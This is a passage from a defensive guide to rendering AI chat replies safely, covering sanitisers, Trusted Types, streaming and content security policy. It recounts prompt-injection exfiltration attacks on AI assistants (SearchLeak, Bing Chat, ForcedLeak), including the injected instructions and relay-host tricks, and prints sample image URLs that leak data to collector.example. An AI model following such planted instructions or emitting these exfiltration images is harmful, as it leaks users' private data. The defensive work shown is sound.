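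A DOMPurify flaw published in March 2026 depends on where the application puts the cleaned HTML. Inside a few elements, such as `noscript`, the browser treats everything as text until it reaches the closing tag. An attacker can write that closing tag into an attribute, where it is harmless in ordinary HTML. If the application puts the cleaned reply inside a `noscript` element, that tag closes the element and the attacker's next tag becomes active HTML. Cure53 had already fixed the same problem for `textarea` in version 3.2.7. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-0540* (2026), five other elements remained exploitable until version 3.3.2. Applications that put replies into an ordinary `<div>` were not exposed. Fluid Attacks' *DOMPurify mXSS via Re-Contextualization*, the finders' own account, rates the flaw's severity as medium.

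Many of the other recent flaws affect only unusual settings. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Dompurify package* has 21 entries for 2026, and seven concern `IN_PLACE`, a mode that cleans existing page elements instead of a string. Others can be exploited only with custom hooks, template languages or a separate flaw elsewhere in the page. OSV's *CVE-2026-65911* (2026) describes a flaw that let settings carry over from one call to the next, which Cure53 regards as an edge case outside what DOMPurify is meant to defend against. An application avoids most of these flaws if it passes DOMPurify a string and uses a short, fixed allowlist.

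DOMPurify still needs updates, and they can be slow to arrive. OSV's *CVE-2026-49978* (2026) describes an `IN_PLACE` flaw that Cure53 fixed in version 3.4.7. That August, Debian's *CVE-2026-49978* listed the copies in two Debian releases, versions 2.4.1 and 3.1.7, as still vulnerable. A copy inside another library can be just as old. On a server, updating DOMPurify does not update jsdom, and Klein and Johns found projects from Mozilla and Grafana Labs that still used the dangerous version 19 of jsdom. Cure53 also advises against using DOMPurify with happy-dom, an alternative to jsdom, because the combination is likely to allow XSS.

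Where DOMPurify cannot run, as in very old browsers, it returns the string unchanged and without warning. An application should check the `isSupported` property and show plain text if it is false.

### Choosing a sanitiser

Security guides often recommend a "vetted" sanitiser without explaining what "vetted" means. At a minimum, the library should work from an allowlist. Java's AntiSamy did not meet this requirement even with its default settings, because it unsafely handled tags that were missing from its configuration.

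The library should also use a real HTML parser, ideally the browser's own. On a server, the parser should at least follow the HTML standard and assume that scripts are on, since browsers parse `noscript` differently when scripts are off. That difference caused several of the bypasses that Klein and Johns found. The sanitiser should also escape text when it writes its output. Programs that clean HTML with search patterns don't meet these requirements.

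Both a sanitiser and its parser need ongoing maintenance. One abandoned JavaScript package in the test, `sanitizer`, had 41 million downloads, and attackers can exploit its flaws indefinitely. The maintainer of bleach, a Python sanitiser, gave it up because its parser was no longer maintained.

A long list of published flaws counts in a library's favour if its developers fixed them quickly, because it shows that capable people attack the library and report what they find. A sanitiser with no advisories may have had no one testing it, as is usually the case when a team writes its own. In *Hand Sanitizers in the Wild*, Klein, Barber and colleagues (2022) studied home-made sanitisers on websites and automatically generated working exploits for 51.3% of the vulnerable ones. Most sanitisers in the study were too specialised to stop XSS in a slightly different setting.

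### The browser's own sanitiser

Browsers have begun to include a sanitiser, which removes the need to keep a library's parser consistent with theirs. Its main method, `setHTML()`, replaces assignment to `innerHTML` and returns nothing. Braun's *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()* explains this choice by comparing the method with a library, which needs one line of code to clean a string and another to insert it. With `setHTML()`, the browser parses the string once for the element that will hold it, cleans the tree and inserts it. This prevents mutation XSS, which depends on a second parse. MDN's *Element* adds that the method first drops elements that are invalid in that place, such as a table column outside a table.

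`setHTML()` always removes event handlers, scripts and embedded frames. Braun, in *Composing Sanitizer configurations*, writes that no configuration is supposed to be able to turn it into an XSS hole. As *setHTML(), Trusted Types and the Sanitizer API* reports, the default also removes images, videos, forms and styles, partly to prevent spoofing and phishing. It is therefore much stricter than DOMPurify's default:

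| In the reply | DOMPurify, default | DOMPurify with the settings above | `setHTML()`, default |
|---|---|---|---|
| Table | Kept | Kept | Kept |
| Event handler | Removed | Removed | Removed |
| Remote image | Kept | Removed | Removed |
| Form | Kept | Removed | Removed |
| Style element | Kept | Removed | Removed |
| False bank link | Kept | Kept | Kept |

The strict default is easy to lose. MDN's *Default sanitizer configuration* notes that when a developer passes in a custom configuration, the browser enforces only the removals needed against XSS. Here, a developer who wants to remove one more element lets images back in:

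```js
reply.setHTML(html);                              // no images

reply.setHTML(html, {
  sanitizer: { removeElements: ["table"] },       // images load again
});
```

A configuration that lists the permitted elements avoids this.

Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* announced Firefox 148 as the first browser with the standard version, and WebDX's *Sanitizer API* dates that release to 24 February 2026. web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* lists support in Chrome and Edge from version 146, and none in Safari. Any public website therefore still needs a library for Safari users. If the application falls back on DOMPurify with default settings, the hostile image will load only in Safari, so `setHTML()` and DOMPurify need the same allowlist. All browsers support the similarly named `setHTMLUnsafe()`, but it is not a safe substitute by default because it removes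 nothing unless it receives a configuration.

### Trusted Types

A good sanitiser does not help if a developer forgets to call it, as happened with Open WebUI's saved prompts. Trusted Types is a browser feature that catches such omissions. A site turns it on through its content security policy. `innerHTML` and similar functions then reject ordinary strings and accept only special objects, which the page must create with a registered function called a policy. Reviewers can check a handful of these policies instead of searching the whole program for unsafe assignments.

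The browser checks that a string has been through a policy, but it does not check what the policy did. Both of these satisfy it:

```js
// protects nothing
trustedTypes.createPolicy("replies", {
  createHTML: (html) => html,
});

// cleans every reply
trustedTypes.createPolicy("replies", {
  createHTML: (html) => DOMPurify.sanitize(html,
    { ...SETTINGS, TRUSTED_TYPES_POLICY: null }),
});
```

The policy that returns its input unchanged turns the hostile reply into a trusted object with its handler intact, and the browser runs the code. Developers write such policies to silence errors when they first turn the feature on. A sample in Cure53's documentation also contains one, which is harmless there because only DOMPurify uses it while cleaning, but it would be dangerous as the page's general policy. The `null` setting in the working version stops DOMPurify from creating its own policy, which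 a strict site would block.

The browser applies a policy named `default` to every ordinary string that reaches `innerHTML`, including strings from old code and outside components. Cure53's separate tool, DOMFortify, sets up such a policy with DOMPurify. The protection still depends on the quality of the sanitiser. Klein and Johns quote a Google report on the company's adoption of Trusted Types, which attributes more than half of the root causes of XSS in browser code to sanitiser bugs.

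The Can I use page *Trusted Types for DOM manipulation* lists support in Chrome and Edge since version 83 and in Safari since version 26. In April 2026 it still showed the feature as off by default in Firefox. A browser without Trusted Types still accepts strings, so the application should call the sanitiser itself for every reply and use Trusted Types to catch places where that call is missing.

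## Cleaning a reply that arrives in pieces

A sanitiser works on a finished string, but most chat applications stream replies, displaying the text while the model is still writing it. The server sends fragments of a few characters, and the page adds each one as it arrives. A fragment can end in the middle of a word or a piece of markdown. In an example from Chrome for Developers' *How LLMs stream responses*, a bold phrase is split across several fragments, so a markdown parser given any one of them alone could not detect the bold text.

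The browser requests images and runs event handlers as soon as they appear, even if the reply is unfinished, and a request can't be recalled once it has been sent. Every intermediate state of the page therefore has to be safe, even one that lasts a few milliseconds. Waiting for the complete reply before displaying it avoids the problem. This suits short outputs such as an image description, but with a long answer it leaves the user looking at an empty window.

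### SearchLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search, which searches a company's mail, meetings and files, made replies safe only once they were finished. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (15 June 2026) describes how the security company combined this weakness with two others to steal data with one click.

The attacker sends the victim a link to the search page on the real Microsoft site, so filters that judge links by domain let it through. The page's address can contain a query, in a parameter named `q`, and Copilot followed any text there as instructions. When the victim clicks the link, Copilot begins work without the victim typing anything. The query in Varonis' demonstration told Copilot to find an email, take its title, replace the spaces with underscores and put the result into the address of an HTML image.

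Microsoft had prepared for HTML in replies. Its guardrail wrapped the output in code blocks so that the browser would display any tags as text, but it did so only after Copilot had finished writing. Until then, the raw HTML went into the DOM:

```
while Copilot writes      the page contains an image element
                          the browser requests the image
after Copilot finishes    the page shows the tag as text
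                          the request has already left
```

The page's content security policy would have blocked an image from the attacker's server. But it allowed every host under `bing.com`, and Bing's "Search by Image" feature fetches a picture from any address it receives. So the image pointed to Bing, with a parameter containing the attacker's address and the stolen title. The browser contacted Bing, whose servers then contacted the attacker's, as the Teams proxy did in EchoLeak. The attacker's log then contained a request for `/Your_Security_Code_847291/img.png`. Login codes often appear in email titles and can stay valid for several minutes, long enough for an attacker to use one.

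According to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*, Microsoft assigned the flaw the number CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install, and said it had no evidence of malicious use. The company rated the flaw critical, although it scored a medium 6.5 out of 10 on the standard severity scale because the victim has to click. Neither Varonis nor The Next Web reports which weakness the fix removed.

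The attack needed all three weaknesses, so removing any one of them would have stopped it:

| Defence | Weakness it addresses | Effect on SearchLeak |
|---|---|---|
| Waiting for the user to submit a query that came from a link | Instructions in the link | Stopped if the user notices the odd query |
| Escaping raw HTML at every update | Live HTML during streaming | Published version stopped, but a markdown image could still load |
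| DOMPurify with default settings at every update | Live HTML during streaming | Gets through, because the defaults keep images |
| A sanitiser that removes images at every update | Live HTML during streaming | Stopped |
| Displaying nothing until the guardrail has run | Live HTML during streaming | Stopped |
| A content security policy without `bing.com` | The relay host | Stopped, unless another permitted host relays |

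Varonis advises developers to sanitise output during rendering instead of afterwards. It also suggests that security teams watch for search links whose `q` parameter contains HTML tags or instructions about image addresses. That may catch copies of the published attack, but an attacker can reword the instructions.

SearchLeak also shows a weakness in allowing only addresses that the user supplied. Copilot received the attacker's text as the user's own query. The rule would have blocked the image address that the model composed, but the attacker could have used the link to supply a ready-made address for each character, as ZombieAgent did in an email.

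### When the live reply and the saved reply differ

GitLab's assistant Duo had a related problem a year earlier. Legit Security noticed that a word's style changed while a reply was arriving, which suggested that the page was interpreting markdown before it had the whole structure. A tag that arrived before its code block had begun could become live HTML. Willison summarises this as streaming bypassing the XSS filter. Better timing alone would not have protected Duo, because DOMPurify's defaults would still have kept an image outside any code block. GitLab's restriction on addresses works at every stage of the stream.

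NVD's *CVE-2026-32626 Detail*, published in March 2026, describes a flaw in AnythingLLM, an application for chatting with one's own documents. The `HistoricalMessage` component passed earlier messages through DOMPurify, but `PromptReply`, which displayed the reply as it arrived, put the HTML straight into the page. The application's own function for markdown images also copied the alternative text into an attribute without escaping it, so crafted text could add an event handler. In desktop versions up to 1.11.1, the attacker's code could then run programs on the user's computer.

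A developer who tested AnythingLLM by reopening a conversation would have seen only the safe version. Using the same rendering function for live and saved replies prevents this kind of mismatch.

### Three ways to clean a growing reply

An application can clean each fragment alone, clean all the text received so far at every update, or use an incremental parser that creates only permitted elements.

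**Cleaning each fragment alone** fails because a tag can be split:

```
fragment 1    <im
fragment 2    g src="https://collector.example/p.png?d=4731">

joined        <img src="https://collector.example/p.png?d=4731">
```

If an `<img>` tag is split across two fragments, a filter that looks for complete tags passes both, and the joined text is a working image. A sanitiser with an HTML parser does better, because it deletes the unfinished `<im` and leaves the rest as harmless text. But it damages a split `<strong>` tag in the same way, and it can't recognise a markdown link whose address is split across two fragments.

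**Cleaning all the text received so far** avoids these errors. At every update, including the last, the application joins the fragments, converts the markdown, sanitises the HTML and replaces the displayed reply. TanStack's *AI Streaming* describes a renderer that reparses the full text every time, so it has no parser state to keep consistent between updates.

The cost grows with the square of the length. Suppose a reply arrives in 1,000 fragments of five characters. The first update processes 5 characters, the second 10, and the last 5,000:

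```
5 + 10 + 15 + ... + 5,000  =  5 × (1,000 × 1,001) / 2
                           =  2,502,500 characters
```

A single pass processes 5,000 characters, about 500 times fewer than reprocessing the whole reply as each piece arrives. With reprocessing, a reply twice as long takes four times as much work to display. Replacing the reply through `innerHTML` also makes the browser rebuild every element. Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) notes that this can include colouring all the code samples again.

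Developers can reduce the amount of processing without making the display less safe. TanStack recommends combining small fragments into fewer updates. With 20 fragments per update, the example needs 50 updates and processes 127,500 characters. The renderer can also reuse finished paragraphs. If the reply consists of ten equal paragraphs and the renderer reparses only the latest one, it processes about 250,000 characters in total, even without batching. It must still revisit an earlier paragraph if a later line defines the address of a link in that paragraph.

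**An incremental parser** keeps track of where it is in the text and reads each character once, so it reads about 5,000 characters in the example. *Streaming Markdown* documents a small JavaScript library of this kind. The library adds new elements to the page without changing existing ones, so users can select and copy text while the rest arrives. Its parser calls a renderer, a set of functions that create elements, add text and set attributes. A developer can replace the renderer with one that creates only permitted elements and checks each address before setting it.

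The library doesn't support HTML tags apart from line breaks, so event handlers can't get in by the usual route. But it creates links and images, and its documentation doesn't mention any check on their addresses. An application that uses the built-in renderer could still leak the door code from the mailbox through an ordinary markdown image.

| Method | Characters processed in the example | Main weakness |
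|---|---|---|
| Each fragment alone | 5,000 | Misses or damages anything split between fragments |
| Whole text at every update | 2,502,500, or 127,500 in batches of 20 | Slow for long replies |
| Incremental parser | 5,000 | Needs address checks in the renderer, and may omit markdown features |

For most chat applications, cleaning the whole text in batches is safer because the application can use the same converter, sanitiser and settings as it does for saved replies. An incremental parser makes more sense for very long replies or slow devices.

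### Problems in Chrome's sample code

Chrome's guidance correctly tells developers to treat model output as untrusted and to sanitise the combined text, but both of its code samples leave gaps. The 2025 sample runs DOMPurify on the markdown received so far. If DOMPurify removes anything, the page stops displaying the reply. Otherwise, the sample passes the latest fragment, unchanged, to streaming-markdown. Because DOMPurify checks the markdown instead of the HTML, it misses a markdown image, which streaming-markdown then creates. The page also stops displaying a harmless answer partway through if the answer shows a script element in a code sample.

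Chrome for Developers' *Built-in AI APIs* (2026) offers a newer sample, which builds the reply off screen and then copies it to the page through a sanitiser. For images, the sanitiser may run too late. A browser starts to load an image when code in the page gives an image element its address, even if the element isn't on the page yet, so the browser can send the request before the sanitiser runs. The sample's allowlist also permits images from any host.

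A more basic problem with the newer sample is that it uses a `sanitize()` method and setting names that do not appear in WHATWG's *Dynamic markup insertion*, the relevant chapter of the HTML standard. In a browser that follows the standard, calling `sanitize()` causes an error. A developer might fix that by passing the same sanitiser to `setHTML()`, but the browser would ignore the unknown names and remove only markup that can run scripts.

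### Links and images that are not finished

The next few characters can change where a link leads. Here the text looks at first like a link to a bank:

```
text so far                                            host at this point

[your bank](https://bank.example                       bank.example
[your bank](https://bank.example.coll                  bank.example.coll
[your bank](https://bank.example.collector.example)    bank.example.collector.example
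```

If a renderer closed the link early to make the reply look tidy, it would briefly show a link to the real bank, then change the destination while the link text stayed the same. A check that approved the early version would have approved a different host from the one in the finished link. Images are worse, because the browser could request each partial address. An image address ending in the door code 4731 could produce requests ending in 4, 47, 473 and 4731.

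The solution is to hold back the address until the link or image is complete. Streamdown's *Unterminated Block Parsing* describes a preprocessor, remend, that immediately closes unfinished bold text and code. It replaces an unfinished link's address with `streamdown:incomplete-link`, which leads nowhere, and shows a loading animation for an unfinished image. Once the closing bracket arrives, the real address goes through the renderer's normal checks. Developers can also set `linkMode` to `text-only` to show unfinished links as plain text. Ant Design X, a library for building chat interfaces, similarly replaces unfinished links and images with placeholder components.

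TanStack leaves an unfinished link as literal text, so the user sees the brackets and part of the address until the link closes. This looks worse but is equally safe, since the text can't start a request.

A bare web address has no closing bracket to mark its end, so an application that turns such addresses into links should wait for a space, a line break or the end of the reply.

Reference-style links can take longer to complete, because the address may be on the last line of the reply. The developer of a streaming parser lists them among the features that cannot fully stream, in the CommonMark forum thread *Would a streaming guidance for CommonMark be useful?* A renderer that reparses the whole reply can show the text immediately and turn it into a link later. streaming-markdown doesn't support reference-style links. If an application uses it for live replies and a full CommonMark parser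 for saved ones, a reference-style image that was harmless text during the chat can load when the user reopens the conversation.

Late characters can also change text that the user has already read. Some markdown parsers treat lines between two rows of dashes at the top of a document as metadata, known as front matter. TanStack recommends switching this off for model output, because when the second row of dashes arrives, the parser could turn the beginning of the reply, which is already on screen, into metadata.

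Holding back an address until it is complete lets the application check the whole address, but the application still needs to check it. Holding back the address would not have stopped SearchLeak, because the browser creates an HTML image only after its tag is complete, and the completed image leaked the data.

### Streaming support in the browser

The HTML standard now includes `streamHTML()`, which cleans HTML as the browser parses it and adds the result to the page step by step. An application that receives markdown must convert it to HTML first. According to Chrome for Developers' *Declarative partial updates* (2026), last updated on 8 September, Chrome and Edge offered the method only behind an experimental setting, with a launch planned for Chrome 155. Firefox and Safari did not support it. Chrome's replacement code for other browsers waits for the whole text before displaying it, and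 it cannot clean the text in Safari on its own.

With no configuration, `streamHTML()` uses the same strict defaults as `setHTML()`. A custom configuration needs to list attributes as well as elements:

```js
const stream = reply.streamHTML({
  sanitizer: new Sanitizer({
    elements: ["p", "strong", "em", "code", "pre", "ul", "ol", "li"],
    attributes: [],
    dataAttributes: false,
  }),
});
```

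Chrome's example sanitiser for basic formatting lists which elements to allow, but not which attributes. Under the standard, it therefore allows every attribute that can't run a script, including `style`, which can load a background image. Chrome's streaming examples are also risky to copy because they use `streamHTMLUnsafe()`, which removes nothing by default.

### Testing every intermediate state

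A test that checks only the finished reply would have passed Microsoft's guardrail. For a renderer that processes the whole text at every update, a developer can test each possible stopping point instead. In this example, `renderReply` stands for the application's complete rendering process, and `checkImage` is the address check shown earlier:

```js
for (let end = 1; end <= reply.length; end++) {
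  const html = renderReply(reply.slice(0, end));
  const page = new DOMParser().parseFromString(html, "text/html");

  for (const image of page.querySelectorAll("img[src]")) {
    if (!checkImage(image.getAttribute("src"))) {
      throw new Error(`Unsafe image after ${end} characters`);
    }
  }
}
```

`DOMParser` creates a separate document in which the browser does not load images, so the test sends no requests. The same loop can check for event handlers, forms and links with forbidden schemes. TanStack already runs its renderer at every character boundary of sample texts, but does so to check that its HTML and React versions produce the same structure.

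An incremental parser writes directly to the page, so it may create an image before any test can inspect the HTML. The developer can instead feed the parser a hostile reply one character at a time in a real browser and record every network request, including those sent before the reply is complete.

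## Content security policy: what the browser may load and contact

A content security policy can stop the browser from loading an unsafe image, even if the image is on the page for only a few milliseconds during streaming or a diagram library creates it after the sanitiser has finished. The browser applies the policy to each request just before sending it, whichever code added the image. *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the World Wide Web Consortium's current draft of the standard, recommends a policy as a second layer that limits the damage when escaping or sanitising fails, not as a replacement for either.

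### How the browser applies a policy

The server sends the policy in an HTTP header, a line of information that arrives before the page itself. A policy is a series of directives separated by semicolons. Each directive is a name followed by a list of permitted sources:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src https://images.assistant.example
```

This page may load images from one host only, and other files from its own origin. Whenever the page requests a file, the browser takes these steps:

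1. It finds the directive for that type of file, such as `img-src` for an image.
2. If the policy has no such directive, it uses `default-src`. If that is missing too, it allows the request.
3. It compares the address with each source on the list. If none matches, it blocks the request before anything reaches the network.
4. If the server answers with a redirect, the browser checks the new address before following it.

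A specific directive replaces `default-src` for its type of file and inherits nothing from it. In the example, the page cannot load images from its own origin, because `img-src` does not list that origin.

| Source | What it matches |
|---|---|
| `'none'` | Nothing |
| `'self'` | The page's own origin |
| `https://images.example` | One host |
| `https://images.example/icons/` | One folder on that host |
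| `*.example.com` | Every subdomain, at any depth, but not `example.com` itself |
| `https:` | Every site that uses `https` |

The last source is useless against image leaks, since an attacker's server can use `https` like any other.

If a policy contains the same directive twice, the browser uses only the first, so adding a stricter `img-src` after an existing one has no effect. If the server sends two separate policies, the browser enforces both, so the second can add restrictions but can't remove any.

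Developers who cannot change the server's headers can put the policy in a `meta` element in the page. The policy then doesn't apply to anything before that element, and the browser ignores a few directives that only work in a header.

### Bing Chat's fix in 2023

Microsoft used a content security policy against image leaks early on. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes how text on a web page, such as a comment or an advertisement, could take over the assistant when a user chatted about that page. Rehberger planted text instructing the model to wait for two turns. The model then wrote an image whose address contained an encoded summary of the page and the chat, along with any passwords on the page.

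Rehberger reported the flaw on 8 April 2023, and Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had fixed it. His earlier attacks no longer worked, and the page now had a content security policy that allowed images from only four hosts: `th.bing.com`, `www.bing.com`, `edgeservices.bing.com` and `r.bing.com`. Bing Chat needed some of these to show pictures it had generated. Rehberger could only see the fix from outside, so Microsoft may have changed other things too.

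The fix was quick to deploy and didn't depend on recognising the attack. Its weakness was the second host on the list, which belongs to Bing, a search engine with many features. Three years later, SearchLeak sent data through one of Bing's image features, which another Microsoft product's policy allowed.

### The directives that matter for model output

| Directive | What it controls | `default-src` applies if it is missing |
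|---|---|---|
| `script-src` | Script files, scripts written in the page, event handlers and `javascript:` links | Yes |
| `style-src` | Style files, style elements and `style` attributes | Yes |
| `img-src` | Images, including backgrounds loaded by style rules | Yes |
| `font-src` | Fonts | Yes |
| `media-src` | Video, audio and subtitles | Yes |
| `frame-src` | Pages embedded in frames | Yes |
| `connect-src` | Connections that scripts open, and the `ping` attribute, which notifies a second address when a user clicks a link | Yes |
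| `form-action` | Where forms may send their contents | No |
| `base-uri` | The `base` element, which changes where relative addresses lead | No |

The `form-action` and `base-uri` directives are easy to forget, and they don't fall back to `default-src`. Even with a policy of `default-src 'none'`, a form in a reply could send a password to any server. If a reply could add a `base` element pointing to `collector.example`, a script that the page later loads from `/app.js` would come from the attacker's server.

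`default-src` is also the only directive that governs prefetching, in which the browser downloads a file early because the page hints that it may be needed. According to W3C, a policy without `default-src` therefore can't prevent exfiltration, even if it forbids all images, scripts and fonts. The browser can prefetch from any host that appears in any of the policy's lists of file sources, so `img-src *` allows prefetching from anywhere on the web.

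### A policy for the chat page

Suppose the assistant at `assistant.example` loads its styles and fonts from its own origin, keeps all its pictures on a separate image host, and exchanges messages with its own server. This policy permits that and little else. The real header goes on one line:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'nonce-{RANDOM}';
  require-trusted-types-for 'script';
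  style-src 'self';
  font-src 'self';
  img-src https://images.assistant.example;
  connect-src 'self';
  form-action 'none';
  base-uri 'none';
  frame-ancestors 'none';
  report-to csp
```

The first line blocks everything, and the later ones make exceptions. Video and frames don't need their own lines because `default-src` already blocks them. `require-trusted-types-for` turns on Trusted Types, so that `innerHTML` rejects ordinary strings. `connect-src 'self'` allows the page's scripts to connect to the assistant's server. Since those scripts also send the user's messages, the page doesn't need ordinary forms and can block them. `frame-ancestors` prevents other sites from embedding the page, and `report-to` makes the browser report what it blocks.

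**Nonces.** The `script-src` line uses a nonce, a random value that the server generates each time it sends the page. The server puts the nonce in the policy and in the `nonce` attribute of its own script elements, and the browser runs only scripts with the matching value. An attacker who plants text in an email can't include the right nonce because the server hasn't generated it yet. W3C requires a new value for every response and recommends at least 128 random bits.

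A nonce applies to script elements, not event handlers, so this policy blocks every inline handler in the page. Developers sometimes allow these handlers again by adding `'unsafe-inline'`. In a policy without a nonce or hash, this also allows the code that a hostile reply would contain. Browsers ignore `'unsafe-inline'` if the same directive has a nonce.

The nonce must also stay secret while the page is open. Browsers hide it from style rules, which could otherwise leak it, as happened in one of the Mermaid flaws. If a server writes old replies directly into the page's HTML, an attacker can also use an unfinished script tag in a reply to absorb the next script element, along with its nonce. Sanitising the reply prevents this, because the sanitiser's output has no unfinished tags.

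If a server sends everyone the same static file, the page can't contain a fresh nonce. The policy can instead list hashes, short fingerprints of the permitted scripts. The browser runs a script only if the hash of its content is on the list.

Some applications have scripts that load further scripts, which a plain nonce would block. Adding `'strict-dynamic'` lets trusted scripts do this, and W3C accepts it as a practical aid but advises developers to avoid it where they can. It is riskier in a chat page than elsewhere because an incremental markdown parser is a trusted script, so the browser also trusts any script element the parser creates. If the parser turned a script tag from a reply into a real element, the browser would run it.

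### The hostile reply under this policy

Suppose every earlier defence has failed and the application puts the whole mailbox reply into the page unchanged. The table adds three items that a hostile reply might also contain:

| In the reply | Directive | What happens |
|---|---|---|
| Table of delivery dates | None | The user sees it |
| Event handler | `script-src` | The code does not run |
| Image with the door code | `img-src` | The browser sends no request |
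| False bank link | None | It works when the user clicks it |
| `javascript:` link | `script-src` | Clicking it does nothing |
| Style element covering the page | `style-src` | The browser ignores it |
| Password form | `form-action` | The user sees the form, but the browser refuses to send it |

The policy stops injected code from running and data from leaking, but it does not stop deceptive content. A false notice still looks as though the assistant wrote it, and a form that is blocked from submitting may still trick someone into typing a password.

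The policy blocks outside pictures even in harmless replies. It can also break the layout of formulas, because KaTeX positions their parts with `style` attributes, and `style-src 'self'` blocks those when the page inserts KaTeX's output as HTML. Adding `style-src-attr 'unsafe-inline'` allows the attributes while still blocking style elements. The sanitiser then has to strip `style` attributes from the rest of the reply, since an attacker could use them to hide a warning or cover a button. They could not load a background from the attacker's server, because `img-src` still applies.

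### Trying a policy out and reading the reports

A strict policy often breaks something its developers forgot about. The `Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only` header lets them find these problems before they enforce the policy. The browser allows requests that the policy would have blocked but reports each one, and the developers fix the policy or the page until the reports stop. A site can send this header alongside the enforcing one to test a stricter policy while its current policy stays in force. A report-only policy doesn't protect users, so the image with the door code would still load and only produce a report.

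The server says where reports should go in a separate `Reporting-Endpoints` header, which gives the name `csp` in the example an address. Shortened, the report about the hostile image looks like this:

```
{
  "type": "csp-violation",
  "body": {
    "documentURL": "https://assistant.example/chat",
    "blockedURL": "https://collector.example/p.png?d=4731",
    "effectiveDirective": "img-src",
    "disposition": "enforce"
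  }
}
```

A chat page with a settled policy should rarely request an image from an unknown host, so a report of such a request may be the first sign of a prompt injection.

The report also contains the door code. The browser removes any user name, password and fragment (the part after a hash sign) from the blocked address before sending the report, but it keeps the path and query, where image leaks put their data. A site that sends its reports to an outside company therefore gives that company the private data that the policy has just protected. The site can avoid this by collecting reports on the application's own server and deleting them soon.

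An attacker can also choose much of a report's contents. W3C warns developers to escape reports before displaying them, or the attack could reach whoever reads the dashboard. For redirected requests, the report gives only the original address, so a site can't use reports to discover where another site sends its users.

### The policy proposed after EchoLeak

In their paper on EchoLeak, Reddy and Gujral recommend denying everything by default and allowing only the company's own origins, with no wildcards. On the page that displays model output, they would forbid all scripts (`script-src 'none'`), plugins, `base` elements, forms and frames. They would use `connect-src` to limit connections to the page's own origin and the company's API server, and restrict images and media in the same way. Any permitted outside request would go through an internal proxy.

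The ban on scripts makes the list unsuitable for an ordinary chat page. `script-src 'none'` blocks the application's own scripts along with the attacker's, and without scripts the page can't stream a reply or sanitise HTML in the browser. The ban suits a page that only displays finished text, such as a saved conversation that the server has already converted to HTML, or a frame that contains only the reply. Two of the list's other recommendations, `connect-src` for an outside API and Trusted Types, are mainly useful on a page that does run scripts, so the full list combines restrictions suited to two different kinds of page.

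Nearly any chat page can use `base-uri 'none'` and `form-action 'none'`, and can also use `frame-src 'none'` until the application needs to embed something. The list should begin with `default-src 'none'`, which Reddy and Gujral describe in words but leave out of their directives. Stripping query parameters from links, as they advise, requires code in the renderer because a policy can only allow or refuse a request.

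Reddy and Gujral include a table of untested defences, in which they expect a strict policy to stop both the automatic image request and the detour through Microsoft Teams. The policy would stop the detour only if none of the hosts it allows can relay data. They also expect a signed media proxy to work, but CamoLeak got data out through one by collecting valid signatures in advance.

### Why lists of permitted hosts fail

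The browser compares a host's name with the names the policy permits, but it can't check what a permitted host does with a request, what scripts it serves, or who currently owns it.

**Relays.** EchoLeak, SearchLeak and CamoLeak all used a permitted host that fetched pictures from other servers. This differs from a redirect in a way that matters for the policy:

```
redirect    browser asks permitted.example for an image
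            permitted.example answers "go to collector.example"
            browser checks collector.example and blocks it

relay       browser asks permitted.example for an image
            permitted.example asks collector.example itself
            permitted.example returns a picture
```

The browser applies the policy to a redirect because it makes the second request itself. In a relay, the permitted host's server makes the second request, which never passes through the browser, so no change to how browsers apply policies could block it. The only remedies are to remove the host from the list or to change what its server will fetch.

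The browser checks an image's original address and any redirects against the content security policy. ChatGPT's `url_safe` service checked the address only once, so Bing links that redirected elsewhere got past it. A policy that did not list the final host would have blocked the redirect to it.

Redirects weaken limits on folders. For example, a policy might permit `https://a.example` and only `https://b.example/icons/`. A direct request for `https://b.example/fetch` fails, but the request succeeds if any page on `a.example` redirects to that address, because after a redirect the browser checks the host and ignores the folder. W3C chose this rule to stop hostile sites from using policies to learn where another site's redirects lead. A folder limit is still worth having, but an attacker who finds a suitable redirect can reach a relay elsewhere on the host.

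The application's own origin can also relay data. If `assistant.example` has a feature that fetches link previews from any address, `img-src 'self'` permits a leak through that feature. An analytics host that only records requests is just as unsafe if anyone can open an account there. The safest entry for `img-src` is a host that serves stored files and ignores the rest of the address.

**Scripts chosen by an attacker.** Listing a host in `script-src` permits every script on that host. Many sites load common libraries from a public content delivery network, and some of these networks serve any package anyone publishes. An attacker who can add a script element to the page can publish a package and load it from the permitted host. The attacker can instead load an old library with a known flaw and exploit that.

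W3C says that lists of hosts and paths are hard to get right for this reason, and cites the 2016 study *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* on the difficulty of deploying a policy that works against XSS. The draft now recommends a "strict" policy, which identifies scripts by nonce or hash, adds `'strict-dynamic'`, and restricts `base-uri`. A nonce solves the problem for scripts because the developer marks each one as trusted. Images have no equivalent, so `img-src` still depends on a list of hosts.

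### ForcedLeak

A permitted host can also change owners. In September 2025 the security company Noma published ForcedLeak, an attack on Agentforce, the AI agent in Salesforce's customer management software. Noma rated its severity 9.4 out of 10, according to the copy of its report posted by Nytro (2025), *ForcedLeak*.

The attack began with Web-to-Lead, a Salesforce feature that puts a contact form on a company's website. Anyone can fill in the form, and Salesforce stores the answers as a lead (a possible customer). Varonis notes that the form's description field accepts up to 42,000 characters, which leaves plenty of room for instructions. Only when an employee asked Agentforce about the lead did the agent read the description and follow the attacker's instructions along with the employee's.

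Willison (2025) reproduces those instructions, a numbered list of questions. The agent was to count the company's leads, say what colour red and yellow make, and list the leads' email addresses with the spaces encoded for use in a URL. It was then to end its reply with an HTML image, labelled as a customer's logo, whose URL contained the email addresses.

Salesforce's policy would have blocked an image from an unknown server, but it allowed every host under `my-salesforce-cms.com`, a domain whose registration had expired. Noma's researchers bought the domain, for about $5 according to Logan Kelly, who was writing for a security vendor. The policy therefore let the browser request an image from a server the researchers controlled, and the request carried customers' email addresses.

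An entry for the single host `cdn.my-salesforce-cms.com` would have failed in the same way as the wildcard entry, because whoever owns a domain decides where all its subdomains lead. Requiring `https` would not have helped either, because the new owner could obtain a valid certificate.

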